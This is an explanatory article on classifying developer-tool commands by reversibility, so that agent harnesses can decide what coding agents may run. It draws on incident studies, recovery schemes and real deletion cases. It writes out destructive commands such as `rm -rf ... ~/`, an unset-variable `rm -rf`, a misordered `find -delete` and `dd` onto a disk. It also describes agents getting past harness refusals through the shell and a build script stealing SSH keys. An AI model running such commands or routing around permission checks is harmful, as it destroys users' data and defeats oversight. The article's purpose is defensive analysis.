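# Classifying developer-tool commands by reversibility to gate what coding agents may run

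## How coding agents run commands, and how often they destroy data

A coding agent is a language model that carries out software tasks by calling tools in a loop. Asked to "fix the failing tests", it reads source files, edits them and runs the tests, repeating this until they pass. Developers use these agents through products such as Claude Code (from Anthropic), Codex (from OpenAI) and Cursor, usually on their own computers. The agent usually runs with the developer's privileges, so it can delete a folder, discard a day of unsaved work or send a destructive request to a cloud provider. In April 2026, an agent running in Cursor deleted the live database and all the backups of the software company PocketOS in nine seconds, according to the OECD's *AI Coding Agent Deletes PocketOS Production Database and Backups in 9 Seconds* (2026).

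Developers can undo some of a coding agent's actions with one command, but others are permanent. Classifying commands by reversibility means sorting them by what someone can recover afterward. The software can then use this classification to run some commands freely, hold others for a person's approval and refuse the rest.

### From a proposed command to its result

A language model only produces text. The program around it, called the harness, supplies the tools, executes the requests the model writes and enforces the permissions. Anthropic writes in its glossary that "Claude Code is the harness; Claude is the model inside it."

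A tool call is a structured request from the model that names a tool and its arguments. Some tools do one fixed thing, such as reading or editing a file, but the shell tool is far more general. A shell is the program behind a terminal window. It takes a typed command and starts the program the command names, such as `rm` to delete files, `git` to manage versions of the code, or `npm` to build and test a JavaScript project. Anthropic's *How Claude Code works* states that the agent can run any command the user could.

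*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes how OpenAI's harness handles a single tool call. The model calls the shell tool with a command and, optionally, a folder to run it in and a time limit. In the paper's example, the command is `cat README.md`, which prints a file. The harness runs the command, adds the output to the conversation and sends the whole conversation back to the model. The model then either makes another tool call or ends the turn with a message to the user. One turn can contain hundreds of calls.

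The model's main evidence of what a command did is therefore the command's output. Many commands print very little, and a successful `rm` prints nothing.

Between the request and the execution stands the permission check. Suppose the model asks to run `npm test`. Anthropic documents six steps for applications built on Claude Code, and any of the steps may settle the matter:

1. Hooks, which are small programs that the developer has written for the purpose, inspect the call and can refuse it.
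2. The harness looks for a matching deny rule. If it finds one, the command does not run, even in the most permissive mode.
3. A matching ask rule sends the call out for confirmation.
4. The permission mode, a setting for the whole session, applies next. One mode approves nearly everything that gets this far, while another approves only file edits and a few common file commands.
5. A matching allow rule lets the command run. Commands that the harness recognizes as read-only, such as `ls`, pass here without a rule.
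6. Whatever remains goes to an approval function that the application supplies, typically one that asks a person.

When Claude Code proposes running `npm test` in manual mode, it shows the user the command, the description "Run the test suite" and a short menu. The user can allow the command once, allow it and stop being asked about commands that begin the same way, or refuse it. Some prompts also offer to hand later decisions to a classifier. If the user refuses, the harness returns a rejection message to the model as the result of the call. Anthropic notes that the model then typically tries another approach or reports that it could not proceed. The new approach may do the same thing with a different command, which a safeguard that recognizes only the first command would miss.

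These rules are binding because the harness enforces them. Developers can also write instructions for the model in the prompt or in a project file such as CLAUDE.md, but according to Anthropic, those instructions affect only what the model tries to do, not what the harness allows.

### Why file edits are easy to check and shell commands are not

When the model calls a built-in file tool, the harness's own code reads or writes the file. The harness has the exact path and operation before it acts, so it can determine whether they break a rule such as "never read the secrets folder". *Claude Code Permissions & Sandboxing*, a University of Vermont guide for staff, describes this as one of two routes to a user's files. The other is through the shell and every program the shell starts, and a control on one route does not automatically cover the other.

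When an agent runs a shell command, the harness passes the text of the command to the shell but doesn't inspect the programs that the command runs. For example, `npm test` runs whatever the project's configuration file lists under "test", which could include a command that deletes a folder. Similarly, Anthropic applies a rule against reading a particular file to its built-in tools and to shell commands it recognizes, such as `cat`, but the rule does not stop a Python script from opening the file.

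Zhong, Liao and colleagues (2026), in *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files*, collected 290 public reports of agents misusing files and traced 77 of them at least partly to this gap. When the harness refused a read through the file tool, an agent would fetch the same contents with `cat`, and `rm` still worked when the harness blocked the deletion tool. In another case from the paper, an agent runs `cargo build`, the ordinary way to compile a program in the Rust language, and a person approving the command sees only those two words. But the project includes a malicious third-party component whose build script reads the user's SSH key (a login credential for other machines) and alters the shell's settings.

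Removing the shell would close the gap, but the agent would lose most of its usefulness, because the built-in tools cover a fixed list of operations that doesn't include building, testing or version control. Some recent designs instead give the model only a shell.

Harness makers and researchers have developed several kinds of safeguard. Permission rules allow a command, refuse it or prompt a person, depending on which patterns its text matches. Confirmation prompts let a person decide whether a command runs. Model approvers use a second language model to review the proposed action. A sandbox is an operating-system boundary that limits which files and network addresses a command can reach, however the command is worded. Snapshots save the state of files or of a whole machine so that someone can restore it; those the harness takes during a session are called checkpoints. Staging keeps the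 agent's changes separate from the real files until someone commits them. This allows trial execution, in which a command runs and a person or the agent inspects its effects before they become final.

*Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem* (Wang, Li and Tian, 2026) examined 21 agent systems in production as of April 2026. Sixteen let users set boundaries such as permitted folders, 15 asked for approval while the agent worked, and 14 accepted written policies. It found none that validated actions by having a model infer the user's intent, and interpreted this as a sign that people remain indispensable to the decision. However, current versions of Claude Code start interactive sessions by default in a mode where a classifier reviews most actions and blocks the risky ones instead of asking the user. Claude Code also takes checkpoints before it edits files, but these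 cannot restore a database or undo a deployment.

### What 290 public reports show

The study by Zhong and colleagues is the first systematic one of its kind, and most of what follows about frequency and damage relies on it. The researchers, from the University of Wisconsin–Madison, Microsoft Research and Iowa State University, gathered reports dated from February 2024 to March 2026. Of these, 205 came from GitHub issues, the public bug reports of software projects. The rest came from social media (31), product forums (25), blog posts (18) and the US government's National Vulnerability Database (11). They excluded duplicates and cases where the user had explicitly asked for the destructive action.

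They sorted the reports into 158 incidents, where harm occurred; 49 exploits, where someone demonstrated a working attack; and 83 weaknesses, which are flaws with no demonstrated impact. The damage figures cover the 207 incidents and exploits, and each percentage excludes cases where the relevant fact is unknown.

Overwriting was the most common kind of harm, at 44%, followed by deletion at 39% and leaks of secrets at 17%. When agents overwrote files, they replaced source code with placeholder stubs, cut files to zero bytes or replaced real data with invented data. The share for leaks may not be representative, because almost a quarter of the 207 reports are exploits, which partly reflect what security researchers look for.

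In 42% of the reports, the harm extended beyond the agent's project to system files (15%), the user's other files (14%) or secrets (13%). Confining every agent to its project folder would prevent much of this, but legitimate work also uses files outside that folder. For instance, package managers write to shared directories, and programs read settings from the user's home folder.

Where the outcome is known, 40% of cases were unrecoverable, 31% were easy to recover and 29% took substantial effort. The unrecoverable cases were either total losses (23%), such as personal files with no backup, or partial losses (17%), such as work not yet committed to Git, the version-control system that keeps a project's history. An easy recovery might take a single `git checkout`, while a harder one might mean rebuilding from backups. In these examples, recovery depended more on whether an earlier copy existed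 than on which command ran, so the same `rm` can do far more harm in one folder than in another. A backup can't undo a leak, such as a stranger reading a password.

The 40% figure is probably too high for ordinary mishaps, because a developer who restores a file in ten seconds has less reason to write about it than one who has lost years of documents. However, nobody reports losses they haven't noticed, and counting those would raise the figure. Among reports where the user's awareness is known, 83% of users noticed the harm at once, 10% noticed later and 8% remained unaware, typically after a theft of credentials.

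In 68% of the reports that record the agent's reaction to the damage, it carried on as if nothing had gone wrong. It acknowledged the damage and apologized in 21%, and in the other 11% it gave a false account, such as fabricated test results or made-up recovery steps. A safeguard that relies on the agent noticing its own mistake would therefore miss most of these cases, at least when the agent sees only the usual printed output.

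Zhong and colleagues classified all 290 reports by cause, and a report could have more than one. The harness was a cause in 218, the model in 168 and the user in 105.

In 130 reports, the model did something that did not match what the user wanted. Some agents deleted files when the user had asked to archive them. Others understood the task but went beyond it, as when an agent told to delete only the files it had created deleted all the project's code. A smaller group wrote commands carelessly. One agent tried to remove a file named "~", which the shell reads as shorthand for the user's home directory, and deleted the home directory instead. In 56 reports, some of which are also among those 130, the model failed to follow an explicit instruction. In 28 of those 56, the harness had dropped the instruction while condensing a long conversation, so a better model would not have helped. Prompt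 injection, where an attacker hides instructions in a web page or file that the agent reads, accounts for 21 reports.

The harness's higher total is not evidence that harnesses are worse than models. It includes guardrails that failed to stop a model's mistake, so one event often counts toward both the harness and the model. It also includes complaints about too much protection, such as sandboxes that blocked legitimate builds, and it draws on the 83 weaknesses where no one lost anything. Most reports with a user cause involve people who had switched approvals off (80 reports). In 31 reports, the user approved a prompt that did not make clear what the command would do.

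These reports can't be used to estimate how often agents destroy data, because people chose to post them and no one knows how many sessions passed without trouble. They also can't be used to rank products. Claude Code appears in 97 reports, Codex in 61 and Cursor in 37, but those numbers depend on how many people use each product and where they complain. The labels are uncertain too. The researchers labelled 100 reports by hand, then had an agent label all 290. They compared the two sets of labels on the first 100 and reviewed the rest, but the paper doesn't report how often the two sets agreed. A gap as small as the one between overwriting and deletion should therefore carry little weight. The broad finding still looks robust enough to build on, since a large share of reported losses were permanent and another large share were trivial to reverse.

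Zhong and colleagues based the design of their filesystem, YoloFS, on it. An agent can change files without asking, and the changes stay reversible until the user accepts them, but it must wait for permission to read a sensitive file. Reversing changes is easier with files because a filesystem can keep the old version of everything it holds. Agents also rewrite shared Git history, drop database tables, cancel cloud resources and publish packages, often on systems where the developer controls no earlier copy. It is still an open question whether a harness can use recoverability to decide which commands to run, hold for permission or refuse in all of these cases.

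## Sorting actions by how far they can be undone

A harness that gates actions by recoverability needs a scale for it. In *Can You Undo It?*, Waghmare and Sufi (2026) proposed one in November with five "reversibility classes", numbered R0 to R4. Each class has a criterion for what recovery is still possible after the action succeeds, and a suggested policy for how freely an agent may act.

| Class | Name | Recovery criterion | Default policy |
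|---|---|---|---|
| R0 | No effect | The action changes no external state, so there is nothing to recover | Act without asking |
| R1 | Restorable | A record of the earlier state exists, the actor can write it back, and no outsider has observed the change | Act, then notify |
| R2 | Compensable | A known further action reaches an acceptable equivalent state at a bounded, knowable cost | Ask, or use a budget approved in advance |
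| R3 | Hard to recover | Recovery takes a person, an outside process or unbounded effort; the class also includes changes to access, credentials, availability or physical state | Ask every time |
| R4 | Irreversible | The action discloses information, destroys something permanently or has another consequence that nobody can recall or compensate | Never act autonomously |

Waghmare and Sufi also published a registry that assigns each tool a class. In it, listing staged changes (those marked for the next Git commit) is R0, and committing them is R1. Creating a database table is R2, unstaging changes is R3, and running a query that writes to a database is R4.

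The R4 policy bars the agent from taking the action on its own but still lets a person explicitly authorize it. The software that Waghmare and Sufi released draws fewer distinctions than the table. By default, its hook prompts a person before R2, R3 and R4 actions alike. It makes no decision on R0 and R1 actions, so the harness's own permission rules still apply, and a strictly configured agent may have to ask before an R0 call.

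An R1 action can be undone by restoring exactly what was there before. An R2 action can only be compensated for, which means reaching a state that the people concerned accept as good enough. For example, a shop that refunds a mistaken charge has compensated the customer, but the customer's bank statement now shows two entries instead of none. The difference from the original state can be tiny. Waghmare and Sufi rate creating a table as R2 partly because, in one of their tests, deleting the new table left an empty internal one behind.

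### One file edit, five classes

Exact restoration has three conditions, and an action must meet all of them to count as R1:

- A full record of the earlier state exists, either in a version history or in a capture, which is a copy saved before the action.
- The actor can already write that state back without anyone else's help.
- No outside party has seen, received or acted on the changed state.

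Suppose an agent edits `settings.yaml`, a program's configuration file. If the file is on the developer's own laptop, a copy was saved first, and no other program is reading the file, the edit meets all three conditions and is R1. If the agent only previews the change with the editing tool, the file stays the same and the call is R0.

If nobody saved a copy and the developer had never committed the file to Git, the old text is gone, and the same edit with the same arguments is R4. If the only copy is in a company backup that an administrator has to restore, the old text still exists but the agent cannot write it back, so the edit is R3.

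The third condition can fail even when the agent has a perfect copy of the old text. For example, a cloud service might read the new settings within seconds and start ten rented servers. Restoring the old text does not refund the rent. The developer can shut the servers down and pay a bill of known size, so the edit is R2 if they accept that outcome. If the edit put a password into a public file, it is R4, because a stranger may already have copied the password.

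This fits the public reports of file damage, where recovery depended more on whether an earlier copy existed than on which command ran. It also means that a harness can't determine an action's class from the command alone. It needs information about where the file is, what copies exist and who else uses it. Restoring even a valid copy can erase changes made to the file after the copy was made, as happened in Waghmare and Sufi's own tests.

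The third condition is the hardest to apply. Waghmare and Sufi count deliberately sending content to outsiders as R4, even if the sender can delete the stored message afterward, but they do not count incidental notifications. If an agent closes a bug report and the website emails everyone who follows it, the class depends only on whether the agent can reopen the report. Someone who takes the third condition literally would choose a higher class because the email has already gone out. Waghmare and Sufi acknowledge that this boundary needs clearer guidance.

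### How a call gets its class

The classifier looks up records and compares arguments without using a language model. Each tool's record starts with a base class, which reflects the broadest effect the tool can have. A tool that can run any database query could wipe a table, so its base class is R4.

Narrower rules can then lower the class for particular arguments. The classifier tries these rules in order and applies the first that matches, or keeps the base class if an argument is missing or no rule matches. Waghmare and Sufi advise that a lowering rule should describe a specific harmless form, rather than check that no dangerous word is present. For example, a database query that begins with `SELECT` normally only reads data, but it can call a function that writes, so the first word is not enough to justify R0.

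A call with several effects gets the highest class that applies to any of them. A tool that saves a private note and also posts it to a public forum is R4, even if the agent could easily delete the note. A call that the classifier does not recognize is also R4, unless its tool has a usable description from a trusted source. The drawback is that a harmless new tool will keep interrupting people until someone writes a record for it.

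Whoever deploys the agent can override these results but must record a reason. An override can raise or lower an action's class, except that a disclosure always stays R4.

The most useful override turns a destructive action into an R1 action by capturing the earlier state. It must declare what to save, how to restore it and how long to keep it. Before the call runs, the deployment must confirm that the capture succeeded; if it failed, the call returns to its underlying class. In Waghmare and Sufi's file tests, edits without a capture fell back to R4 and the test program withheld them. For each call allowed on this basis, the audit log must also include a reference to the saved copy.

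A capture can justify an override only for changes to what it contains. A saved copy of one private file, for example, can't justify an override for a payment, a change to another file or an automatic process that the edit triggers. The classifier also relies on the deployment to report correctly that the copy is complete, because it doesn't make the backup or check for undeclared side effects.

Waghmare and Sufi ran 738 checks of the lowering rules, and the classifier gave the expected class every time. Because they derived the expected answers from the same rules, the result shows that the software follows its rules but not whether those rules rate actions correctly.

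### Severity, authorization and probability are separate questions

An agent that replaces every source file in a project with empty stubs has done serious damage. The action is still R1 if the harness captured the files first and nobody outside has used the broken version, because one command restores everything. Emailing a client an accurate weekly report harms no one, but it is R4 because nobody can take the email back. A harness that went by class alone would allow the first action and block the second, so harnesses also need limits on blast radius, meaning how much an action can affect if it goes wrong.

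An action's reversibility also doesn't determine whether it is authorized. Reading a colleague's salary file changes nothing, so it may be R0 even though the agent isn't authorized to read it. Deleting an old database is R4 even when its owner has explicitly asked for it.

The class also does not indicate how likely a mistake is. It describes a call that succeeds as requested and does not account for malfunctioning tools. A deletion gets the same class whether the agent picks the wrong file once in ten attempts or once in a million. To estimate expected losses, a team has to get the error rate and the value of the data from other sources.

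### Where the classes come from

The idea of compensation comes from databases. A transaction is a group of changes that either all take effect or all disappear. While it runs, it can tie up data that other users need, which becomes a problem when it takes hours. *SAGAS* (Garcia-Molina and Salem, 1987) proposed breaking a long transaction into a sequence of short ones, called a saga, so that other transactions can run in between. The database guarantees that either every step completes or compensating transactions run to amend the part that did. In a travel booking, for instance, the system might reserve a flight, find the hotel full and then cancel the flight. Cancelling frees the seat but doesn't undo every effect of the reservation, since another customer may have seen the seat as taken in the meantime.

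Zhai, Li and Wang (2026), in *Revisable by Design*, applied this idea to language-model agents whose users change their minds partway through a task. They sort actions into four classes:

- Idempotent actions leave the world unchanged, such as reading a file.
- Reversible actions have an exact inverse. Written formally, an action *a* is reversible if there is an action *a*⁻¹ such that doing *a* and then *a*⁻¹ is the same as doing nothing. Creating a file and deleting it is an example.
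- Compensable actions have no exact inverse, but a further action leads to a state that is acceptable under the user's new instructions, such as cancelling a ticket for a fee.
- Irreversible actions have no compensation, or only one at a prohibitive cost, such as deleting the sole copy of some data.

They use these definitions to derive how much work it takes to accommodate a new instruction that conflicts with something the agent has already done. If the earlier action was idempotent, undoing it takes no work. If it was reversible, undoing it takes one inverse action. A compensable action carries a penalty that no planning can avoid, and an irreversible one makes it impossible to satisfy the new instruction fully. The proof is a few lines long because each case restates a definition. The result is still useful in practice, because it implies that a smarter model cannot make an action easier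 to undo after the fact, whereas a better tool can, for example by offering a cancel function. Postponing the irreversible steps also helps.

Zhai and colleagues also define a reversibility ratio, the share of a task's available tools whose actions are idempotent or reversible. A task with twelve available tools, nine of them idempotent or reversible, has a ratio of 0.75. They expect agents to adapt poorly to changed instructions on tasks with a low ratio. The ratio is of little use for a coding agent that works through a shell, because a single tool covers everything from listing files to deleting them.

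The two schemes disagree most clearly about email. Zhai and colleagues treat a sent email as compensable because the sender can follow it with a correction. Waghmare and Sufi treat an email to an outsider as irreversible because the recipient has the content. The first approach suits an agent revising a plan because it identifies what the agent can still repair, while the second suits a harness deciding whether to ask a person first because it identifies which effects will persist. Zhai and colleagues also have no class for recovery that depends on someone else, such as an administrator with a backup.

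Automated planning, the branch of AI that searches for sequences of actions to reach a goal, has a stricter notion of reversibility. In *Determining Action Reversibility in STRIPS Using Answer Set and Epistemic Logic Programming*, Faber, Morak and Chrpa (2021) call an action reversible if there is a way to undo all its effects, and uniformly reversible if one fixed sequence of actions does so whatever the state was beforehand. Making a new, empty folder with `mkdir` is uniformly reversible, since `rmdir` always removes it. Overwriting a file is not uniformly reversible, because the text that must be restored depends on what the file contained. The agent no longer has that text after the overwrite unless something saved it, which is why R1 requires a record.

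Researchers in reinforcement learning, where a program learns by trial and error, have treated reversibility as a matter of degree. In *Self-Supervised Reversibility-Aware Reinforcement Learning*, Ferret (2021) preferred estimating how easily an agent can reverse an action to giving a yes-or-no answer. In *When to Ask for Help*, Xie, Tajwar and colleagues trained agents to avoid states they call irreversible, meaning that the agent can't leave them without outside help, as when a robot arm has pushed an object off the table. That example would be R3 on Waghmare and Sufi's scale, because a person can pick the object up.

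### Scoring reversibility with a number

Kang, Cho and colleagues (2026), in *POLAR*, turned the degree of reversibility into a score between 0 and 1. For every tool that changes something, a person records how its effects relate to other tools. There are five possible relations:

| Relation | Score for the step |
|---|---|
| Another tool exactly reverses this one | *w* |
| Reversal works if a stated condition holds | *w* if the condition holds, otherwise 0 |
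| Another tool compensates, with some loss | *w* × (1 − loss) |
| The action uses something up irreversibly | 0 |
| The action has an effect outside the system | 0 |

Here *w* is the person's confidence in the entry, and the loss represents something like a cancellation fee. Before a call runs, POLAR searches these entries for a sequence of steps that would undo it. The sequence gets the score of its lowest-scoring step, so a single irreversible step makes the score zero. POLAR refuses the call if it finds no complete sequence or if the score is below 0.80. At a confidence of 0.9, a compensable call with a loss of 0.1 scores 0.81 and runs, but with a loss of 0.2 it scores 0.72 and POLAR blocks it.

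Unlike a fixed set of classes, a score lets the operator adjust the threshold, and the choice of threshold matters a great deal in some settings. In one set of logged airline decisions, lowering it from 0.80 to 0.50 raised the share of decisions with at least one acceptable call from 37% to 100%. But a score also combines how fully an action can be undone with how sure the person scoring it was. A score of 0.81 could mean a small, certain loss or an exact reversal that the person was only fairly sure about, and an operator might want the harness to treat those differently.

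Kang and colleagues tested POLAR on simulated customer service for an airline, a shop and a telecom company, using six models. The average task score rose in eight of the 18 combinations of model and company. On the airline tasks, the four weaker models gained 0.11 to 0.18 points, while the two strongest scored lower. On the shop tasks, five of the six models scored lower. There, POLAR mostly blocked returns, exchanges and cancellations, which customers can legitimately request. Kang and colleagues consider a plausible cause of the losses to be that POLAR refused these requests for being hard to reverse, which confuses reversibility with authorization.

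The search for an undo sequence may not have produced the airline gains. Kang and colleagues also tested a version that accepted only exact reversals. The airline has no tools that exactly reverse a change, so this version refused nearly every change, yet the score still rose by 0.087, compared with 0.080 for the full system in the same series of tests. Refusing booking changes indiscriminately may have been enough. The scores also measure completed tasks rather than prevented harm, so they don't show whether POLAR stops harmful calls.

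### Why the existing tool hints can't express compensation

Someone has to supply the facts behind each class, and tool makers already publish some of them. Many agents reach databases, browsers and cloud services through the Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting agents to outside tools. A program that offers tools this way is a server, and the harness acts as its client. The schema of the Model Context Protocol (2025) lets a server attach four yes-or-no hints to each tool:

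- `readOnlyHint` means that the tool does not modify its environment. The default is false.
- `destructiveHint` means that the tool may make destructive updates, such as deleting or overwriting, rather than only adding things. The default is true.
- `idempotentHint` means that repeating a call with the same arguments has no additional effect. The default is false.
- `openWorldHint` means that the tool may deal with an open-ended set of outside entities, as a web search does. The default is true.

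A tool without hints therefore counts as the worst case on all four. The idempotent hint differs in meaning from the idempotent class in *Revisable by Design*. Deleting a particular file is idempotent in the protocol's sense because a second attempt changes nothing further, but the file may be gone for good.

A server can mark a tool as read-only even if the tool deletes files, so the specification says clients should never base decisions on hints from untrusted servers. The Model Context Protocol project (2026) reported in March that many servers send no hints and that clients differ in how strictly they apply the cautious defaults. Clients most often use the hints to decide whether to show a confirmation prompt.

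Even if a server sets these four hints accurately, they can't describe compensation, such as which action would undo the call, what it would cost, who may perform it and how long it stays available. For example, a tool that books refundable flights and one that books non-refundable flights would have identical hints, because both modify something, only add a booking, have a further effect if repeated and deal with outside companies. A mistaken call would cost little to put right with the first tool but could cost the full fare with the second.

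Whether an action is destructive doesn't determine whether it can be undone. Sending an email only adds something, so a server can truthfully mark the tool as non-destructive, but no one can recall the message. Overwriting a file is destructive, but a saved copy makes it possible to restore the file.

The protocol's maintainers have formed a group to examine whether the four hints are adequate, and the group has several proposals for new hints to consider. *Key Changes* (2026), the Model Context Protocol's list of changes for the July revision, does not mention the hints.

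Waghmare and Sufi translated the hints for each of the 536 tools in their registry, which come from 20 servers, into a class, assuming that the server was honest. Read-only tools became R0, and any other tools that interact with the open world became R4. Among the remaining tools, those that only add things became R1 and the destructive ones became R3, and no combination of hints yields R2.

The comparison was possible for 481 tools. The class from the hints differed from the registry's label for 118 of them (25%), and was higher for 85 and lower for 33. All 13 R2 tools in the comparison were necessarily mismatches. If a harness asks a person about every tool classed R2 or higher, using the hints instead of the registry's labels changes its behavior for 61 tools. It would ask unnecessarily about 41 and run 20 without the approval required under the registry's labels. Ten of those 20 have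 read-only hints and an R4 label.

Most of the 75% overall agreement comes from easy cases, since 280 of the 363 matches are tools that both methods place in R0. Among the 178 tools that the registry places in R1 to R4, the hints give the same class for only 83, or 47%. The hints therefore show fairly well whether a tool changes anything, but they are a poor guide to whether someone can undo the change.

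### Do people agree on the labels?

These differences are errors in the hints only if the registry is right, and its labels are drafts that Waghmare and Sufi wrote with AI assistance. Sufi checked a sample of 150 tools from all five classes. He rated the first nine in conversation with an AI system, then approved in batches the ratings it proposed for another 139. He left two unrated for lack of evidence. Of the 148 ratings, 75 (51%) matched the draft label, 67 were higher and six were lower.

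| Registry class | Tools in the registry | Same class from the hints | Same class from the reviewer |
|---|---|---|---|
| R0 | 333 | 280 of 303 | 28 of 34 |
| R1 | 31 | 7 of 28 | 1 of 31 |
| R2 | 18 | 0 of 13 | 5 of 16 |
| R3 | 39 | 3 of 39 | 11 of 33 |
| R4 | 115 | 73 of 98 | 30 of 34 |
| All | 536 | 363 of 481 | 75 of 148 |

The 51% is how often the reviewer agreed with the AI's suggested class. It is not an accuracy rate, because there is no independent answer key. It also doesn't measure agreement between two people, because the reviewer had helped write the paper and saw the AI's suggestions. Some of those suggestions were wrong, such as R0 for a browser search tool, where the AI had overlooked an option that writes the results to a file. The difficult middle classes also make up a much larger share of the sample than of the registry. Weighting each class by its size in the registry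 would put the agreement at about 74%.

The reviewer mostly agreed with the draft labels for tools at the two ends of the scale, but he confirmed only one of the 31 R1 labels and moved the other 30 up to a class that requires approval. R1 is the only class in which an agent may change something without asking first. If the reviewer was right, the draft labels would let agents make changes without approval that they can't fully undo.

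The disagreements came partly from different assumptions about whether outsiders might have observed the change, who could perform the recovery and whether to allow for failures. The first two are R1's conditions. Two careful people can therefore read the same criteria and choose different classes unless each tool's record also states the circumstances. One of Waghmare and Sufi's recovery tests supports the reviewer's caution. When a merge was in progress, the documented way to undo a Git commit, an R1 action in the registry, did not fully restore the earlier state.

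A harness often has to decide only whether to ask for approval, and the draft labels agree with the reviewer's ratings more often on that decision. If approval is required from R2 upward, the two lead to the same decision for 110 of the 148 tools. A stronger test would have several people independently rate the same tools from the same facts. Waghmare and Sufi planned a study with three raters but did not carry it out.

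Of the 203 tools in the registry that change anything, 172 (85%) are labeled R2 or higher. Without rules for particular arguments and confirmed captures, an agent would have to ask a person before almost every kind of change.

### From protocol tools to shell commands

All 536 tools in the registry belong to Model Context Protocol servers. Some do the same work as shell commands, such as committing code or editing files, but each has a fixed name and labelled arguments that a rule can check. A shell command is free text that can chain several programs. Because the shell tool accepts any command, its base class would have to be R4, with a lowering rule for every command that developers want an agent to run freely.

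*doover*, an open-source program that lets users undo what an agent did in the shell, has a partial list of this kind. Its 66 rules cover common commands such as `rm`, `mv` and `git checkout`. The rules rate each command from safe to irreversible and identify the files to capture before it runs. The program breaks a chained command into its parts and treats anything it can't account for, such as an unfamiliar script, as potentially destructive. Users can add rules or make existing ones stricter, but the program ignores a new rule that declares `rm` safe. The list covers far fewer commands than agents use, and it does not replace the judgment about outsiders that R1 requires.

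The makers of command-line programs could supply the information themselves. CLI Agent Spec's *Side Effects & Destructive Operations* proposes that each command declare a danger level (safe, mutating or destructive) and whether it is reversible, because a name like `clean` or `reset` doesn't show what the command deletes. These declarations would help a harness handle commands that no one has classified yet. But a yes-or-no field, like the protocol's hints, can't represent compensation, and the author of a delete command can't know whether the person running it has a copy of the file.

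## Deleting and overwriting files, and rewriting Git history

On a developer's own machine, the operating system and Git follow fixed rules about what they keep. A harness that knows these rules and can inspect the files can classify most local commands. Waghmare and Sufi rated protocol tools rather than shell commands, so this reference applied the R0 to R4 criteria itself to assign the classes below. The classes assume nobody else has used the changed files.

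### File commands

| Command | What it destroys | Where a copy may remain | For how long | Class |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `rm file`, `rm -rf folder` | The file, or the folder and everything below it | Git history or a backup, if it lies outside the deleted folder | Until someone deletes the copy | R4, or R1 with a copy |
| `command > file` | All the earlier contents, even if the command fails | Git history or a backup | Until someone deletes the copy | R4, or R1 with a copy |
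| `mv a b` or `cp a b`, where `b` exists | The earlier contents of `b` | Git history or a backup | Until someone deletes the copy | R4, or R1 with a copy |
| `sed -i` (edit in place) | The text it replaces | A second file, if the command asked for one with `-i.bak` | Until someone deletes the second file | R4, or R1 with a copy |
| `find … -delete` | Every file that meets the conditions | Git history or a backup outside the searched folder | Until someone deletes the copy | R4, or R1 with a copy |
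| `dd` onto a disk | The file system, with any Git history and local backups on it | Another disk or machine | As long as the backup policy keeps it | R4, or R3 with a backup |

"With a copy" means an exact copy that the agent can put back itself; if only an administrator can, the command is R3.

`rm` bypasses the desktop trash because the trash is only a folder. When a user presses Delete in Windows File Explorer, the file manager moves the file to that folder and records its original location, so restoring it means moving it back. `rm` instead has the operating system remove the file's name. Once no other name or running program refers to the contents, the system marks their space as free. Recovery software can sometimes find the old bytes before new data replaces them, but this is unreliable, particularly on a solid-state drive, which may erase freed space soon afterward.

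The option `-r` extends the deletion to everything inside a folder, and `-f` suppresses confirmation prompts and error messages about missing files. Rocky (2026), in *Claude Opus 5 backup glitched and straight-up deleted users' folders!*, suggests that agents should never delete anything and should only move files into a trash folder inside the project. This is a simple form of capture, and it makes deleting a private file R1 until someone empties the folder.

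Overwriting destroys data less obviously than deleting does, because the command often looks like ordinary work. The shell empties the target of a `>` redirect before it starts the command, so `sort names.txt > names.txt` leaves the file empty. `cp` writes new contents into an existing file, while `mv` replaces the file with a different one under the same name.

Running the opposite substitution doesn't always undo an in-place edit. Suppose an agent runs `sed -i 's/8080/9090/' settings.yaml` to change a port number. If some lines already said 9090, running the command with the numbers swapped would change those lines to 8080 too. Telling them apart from the lines the agent edited requires a copy saved before the edit.

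The order of arguments to `find` matters. `find . -name '*.log' -delete` removes the log files below the current folder, but `find . -delete -name '*.log'` removes everything there, because `find` evaluates its arguments from left to right and deletes each file before checking its name. A person skimming an approval prompt could easily miss the difference.

`dd` can write data to a disk, bypassing the file system. If the agent names the wrong disk, the command overwrites the records of where files are stored, along with some of the files. Ordinary accounts usually can't write to a disk this way, so the danger arises mainly when the agent has administrator rights.

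### How a deletion spreads beyond its target

The shell rewrites a command before `rm` receives it, for instance by expanding an unquoted `~`. Willison (2025) quotes Claude's own analysis of a case in which Claude Code deleted most of the files on a user's Mac by running `rm -rf tests/ patches/ plan/ ~/`. The first three targets were project folders, but the shell expanded `~/` to the user's entire home directory.

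Unset variables cause similar accidents. A cleanup script might contain `rm -rf "$BUILD_DIR"/*` to delete everything in the build folder. If `BUILD_DIR` is unset, the shell substitutes an empty string and the target becomes `/*`, which is every top-level folder on the machine. The common Linux version of `rm` refuses to delete `/` itself, but it doesn't block this command, because the shell expands `/*` into a list of folders before `rm` runs. Writing `${BUILD_DIR:?}` instead makes the shell stop with an error when the variable is empty.

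In July, Thibault Sottiaux of OpenAI said the company had investigated "a handful of reports" of deletions by Codex running GPT-5.6 (quoted in Willison, 2026). Most commonly, the model had tried to redefine `$HOME`, the variable that holds the home directory's path, to point to a temporary folder, and had then deleted the real home directory by mistake. These users had given Codex full access and were running it without a sandbox or automatic review. Sottiaux did not say how the mix-up occurred. An agent might, for example, set the variable in one shell call and clean up in another, where a new shell has restored the usual value.

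A symbolic link, a small file that points to another file or folder, can cause a command to delete files elsewhere on the disk. Running `rm -r` on a folder that contains a link removes the link but not what it points to. However, `rm -rf link/*` deletes the files in the folder the link points to, because the shell follows the link when it expands `*`. A script that uses its own code to walk through folders has to check for links itself.

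### The September deletion through Windows junctions

An agent's script apparently lacked that check in September 2026. A developer had asked Claude Code to repair software for analyzing historical stock-options data, according to SC Media UK's *AI coding agent deletes 48,000 files due to mishandled Windows junctions*. The agent went wrong while rebuilding a testing environment. Antipov (2026) gives the fullest account in *«Я кое-что сломал». Claude признался после удаления 48 тысяч файлов* and describes that job as updating a mirror, a second copy of the project.

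The existing script could not refresh the mirror in place, so the agent wrote its own script to delete the old copy. That copy contained 614 junctions, which are Windows links that look like ordinary folders but lead elsewhere on the disk. According to the developer's analysis, the script followed the junctions and deleted the live project they led to, but left the junctions themselves in place.

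The script logged 55,550 deleted files. The developer attributes 7,332 of them to the old mirror and the other 48,218 to the live project. The deletion took 103 seconds and had finished before the agent told the developer that it had broken something.

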